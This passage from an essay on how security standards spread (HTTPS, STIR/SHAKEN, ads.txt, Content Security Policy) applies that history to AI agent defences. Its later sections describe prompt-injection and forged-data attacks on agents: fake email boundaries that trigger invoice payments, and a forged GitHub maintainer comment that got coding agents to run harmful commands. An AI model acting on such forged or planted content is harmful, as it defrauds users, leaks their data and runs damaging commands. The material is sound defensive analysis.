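HTTPS stalled for years while website owners had to buy and install certificates. In late 2015, when about 40% of the pages Firefox users loaded came over HTTPS, a nonprofit service called Let's Encrypt began issuing certificates free and automatically. Bandara and colleagues attribute the later spread of HTTPS to free certificates and to support from hosting companies, which could turn on HTTPS for their customers without requiring them to learn how it worked.

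Browser makers put pressure on sites to encrypt their pages. In 2017 Chrome began to mark unencrypted pages that asked for passwords or card numbers as "Not secure", and in July 2018 it extended the warning to all unencrypted pages. Ana's customers could now see the warning, which gave her a reason to switch that was unrelated to the internet's general security. Because encryption became much cheaper and a few browser makers also penalised sites without it, it is hard to say how much either change would have achieved alone. The 2024 mail rules imposed a penalty too, but large organisations still had to find all their sources of mail before they could safely enforce DMARC.

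American phone companies adopted caller-ID authentication because the law required it. Congress passed the TRACED Act in December 2019, and regulators gave large companies until 30 June 2021 to introduce a system called STIR/SHAKEN on the internet-based parts of their networks. Smaller companies got more time. The caller's phone company signs a statement of the number and grades its confidence A, B or C. An A means the company knows the customer and has confirmed their right to the number. A B means it knows only the customer, and a C means it knows only where the call entered its network. The recipient's phone company checks the signature.

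Older telephone equipment drops the signature that authenticates a call. TransNexus, which sells call-authentication software, found in 2024 that only about two in five calls still had a signature when they arrived. Unwanted callers can also rent real numbers, and a phone company that profits from their calls may be willing to vouch for them. The system therefore has the same weakness as SPF, which spammers could pass by using their own domains. The law got phone companies to install the system, but it produced no clear fall in robocalls. YouMail, which sells call blocking, estimated that Americans received an average of more than four billion robocalls a month in every year from 2021 to 2024, though that total includes wanted calls such as appointment reminders.

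The ads.txt file spread much faster than email authentication. In 2017 fraudsters were selling advertising space that they falsely claimed was on well-known websites. The IAB Tech Lab, a standards body for online advertising, asked publishers to list their authorised sellers in a text file so that buyers could check offers against it. That autumn Google's advertising tools began blocking sellers missing from a publisher's file. Bashir and colleagues found that by 2019 more than 60% of publishers among the 100,000 most popular websites had an ads.txt file, but that large advertising exchanges were still buying space from unauthorised sellers.

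Publishers had a strong reason to act because every fake sale could take money from them. They only had to edit a short text file, and a few big buyers checked it. Labeling untrusted reviews would take about as little work, but Ana doesn't lose a sale to a competitor each time she leaves out a label.

All three of these standards eventually spread, so choosing them biases the comparison towards success. Iqbal notes that websites have adopted another standard, Content Security Policy, slowly and incompletely. It lets a site specify where scripts on its pages may come from, so that browsers can refuse a script an attacker has inserted. It may be the best match for labels that protect agents, because in both cases the site has to describe its own pages in detail to protect its visitors from someone else's content. Browsers don't warn people about sites without such a policy, and advertisers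 don't refuse to pay those sites.

Email authentication therefore looks fairly typical of protections that people can ignore without an immediate loss, though its twenty-year timetable is less typical. Most large publishers adopted ads.txt, which took little work and had powerful companies insisting on it, within about two years.

### Whether agents can protect themselves

A mail server mainly decides whether to deliver a message. Once the recipient has read it, the server can't stop them from believing it. An agent's operator can still intervene after the agent has read something, by limiting what the agent may do with it. If such limits work well enough, agents might not need scores or declarations from the rest of the web.

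*Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body for AI developers, lists the main ways to protect an agent. It recommends giving the agent only the access its task requires, running it in an isolated environment, and asking the user to confirm serious or irreversible actions. It also advises developers not to rely solely on detecting attacks.

One of its principles concerns three abilities: reading private data, reading text from strangers and communicating with the outside. An agent with all three can leak secrets to an attacker. Suppose Ana's agent reads her inbox, and a stranger sends a message instructing it to forward her bank statements. The attack fails if the agent can't see the statements, never reads strangers' messages, or can send mail only to approved addresses. But a user who wants help answering new customers needs an agent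 with all three abilities, and the forum accepts that restrictions make agents less useful.

One of the forum's suggestions is to let an agent read mail only from trusted senders. That rule gives little protection if a stranger can forge a trusted address, so the agent's defence depends on the email authentication standards SPF, DKIM and DMARC.

Iqbal goes further with INTACT, a system that assumes an attacker can persuade the model of anything. Most agents give the model a whole page at once, so a sentence in a review can persuade it to press the payment button. INTACT shows the model one element of the page at a time, such as a heading, a link or a button. When the model considers the review, it can propose an action only on the review, and ordinary software blocks clicks on plain text. When the model later considers the payment button, it sees a log of the steps already planned, such as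 choosing a cake, but not the review.

Iqbal tested this on 1,091 real webpages with added attacks. A conventional planner let through 73.1% of the attacks, while INTACT's planner let through 12.8%. The attacks that got past INTACT's planner could at most produce a request for the user's consent. Isolation disrupted 3.7% of the tasks. Users would still have to read the requests, and if they approved a quarter of the bad ones without thinking, about 3.2% of all the attacks would succeed.

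INTACT doesn't need websites to label anything. Iqbal chose this design partly because sites had been so slow to adopt protections such as Content Security Policy. The history of web standards is therefore a reason to put defences inside the agent.

### Forged facts instead of planted orders

*Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) describes a weakness in many other defences. Most of these defences try to stop an agent from treating a stranger's text as an instruction, but the paper's attacks instead make that text look like trustworthy data.

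Suppose Ana asks her agent to pay any invoice her accountant has approved. Her mail software gives the agent each message with a sender, a subject and a body. An attacker sends a message whose body imitates the end of one email and the start of another, with the accountant named as the sender of the second. The software correctly treats all of this as the body of one message, but the agent's model may interpret it as two. The agent would then follow Ana's instruction and pay an invoice that her accountant never approved.

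The imitation doesn't have to be exact. A conventional program relies on precise punctuation to separate fields, but a language model infers where the boundaries are and can accept punctuation that a conventional program would reject. In tests on six models without special defences, these forgeries succeeded 31% to 43% of the time in JSON, a common data format, and 33% to 100% of the time in data that represented web pages.

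The researchers then compared the two kinds of attack against leading defences for agents. Planted instructions succeeded at most 0.7% of the time, and forged data up to 50% of the time, though the attacker has to know how the agent arranges its data. Still, the attacks worked against real products. Choi and colleagues could make web agents, including Claude in Chrome, click on something the attacker had chosen. By posting a GitHub comment that appeared to come from the project's maintainer, they also got coding agents, including OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI, to run harmful commands. Anthropic, OpenAI and Google have acknowledged the problems.

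A near-zero success rate for planted instructions is therefore weak evidence that an agent can read anything safely. The forged comment also closely resembles email's original problem, in which anyone could write any name in the From line. GitHub records who posted the comment, but the agent loses that information when it combines the comment and its author's name into one text for the model.

A reputation score for GitHub wouldn't help, since GitHub is a legitimate site. A label that separates users' comments from the site's own information could help, but only if ordinary software acts on it before the model reads the page. If the operator passes the label to the model as text, an attacker can try to forge it too. INTACT's design should prevent the forged clicks, because software, not the model, tracks which element each action belongs to. Forged facts within a single element might still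 mislead the model.

Defences inside the agent help least when the site itself is fraudulent. Iqbal leaves hostile site owners out of INTACT's scope. When the Comet browser bought a watch from a fake Walmart store, nothing had diverted the agent from its task, because the user had asked it to buy the watch there. A shopping agent has to be able to pay, and asking the user to confirm a purchase helps only if the user notices that the store is fake. A warning from someone who had already checked the domain could have stopped the purchase.
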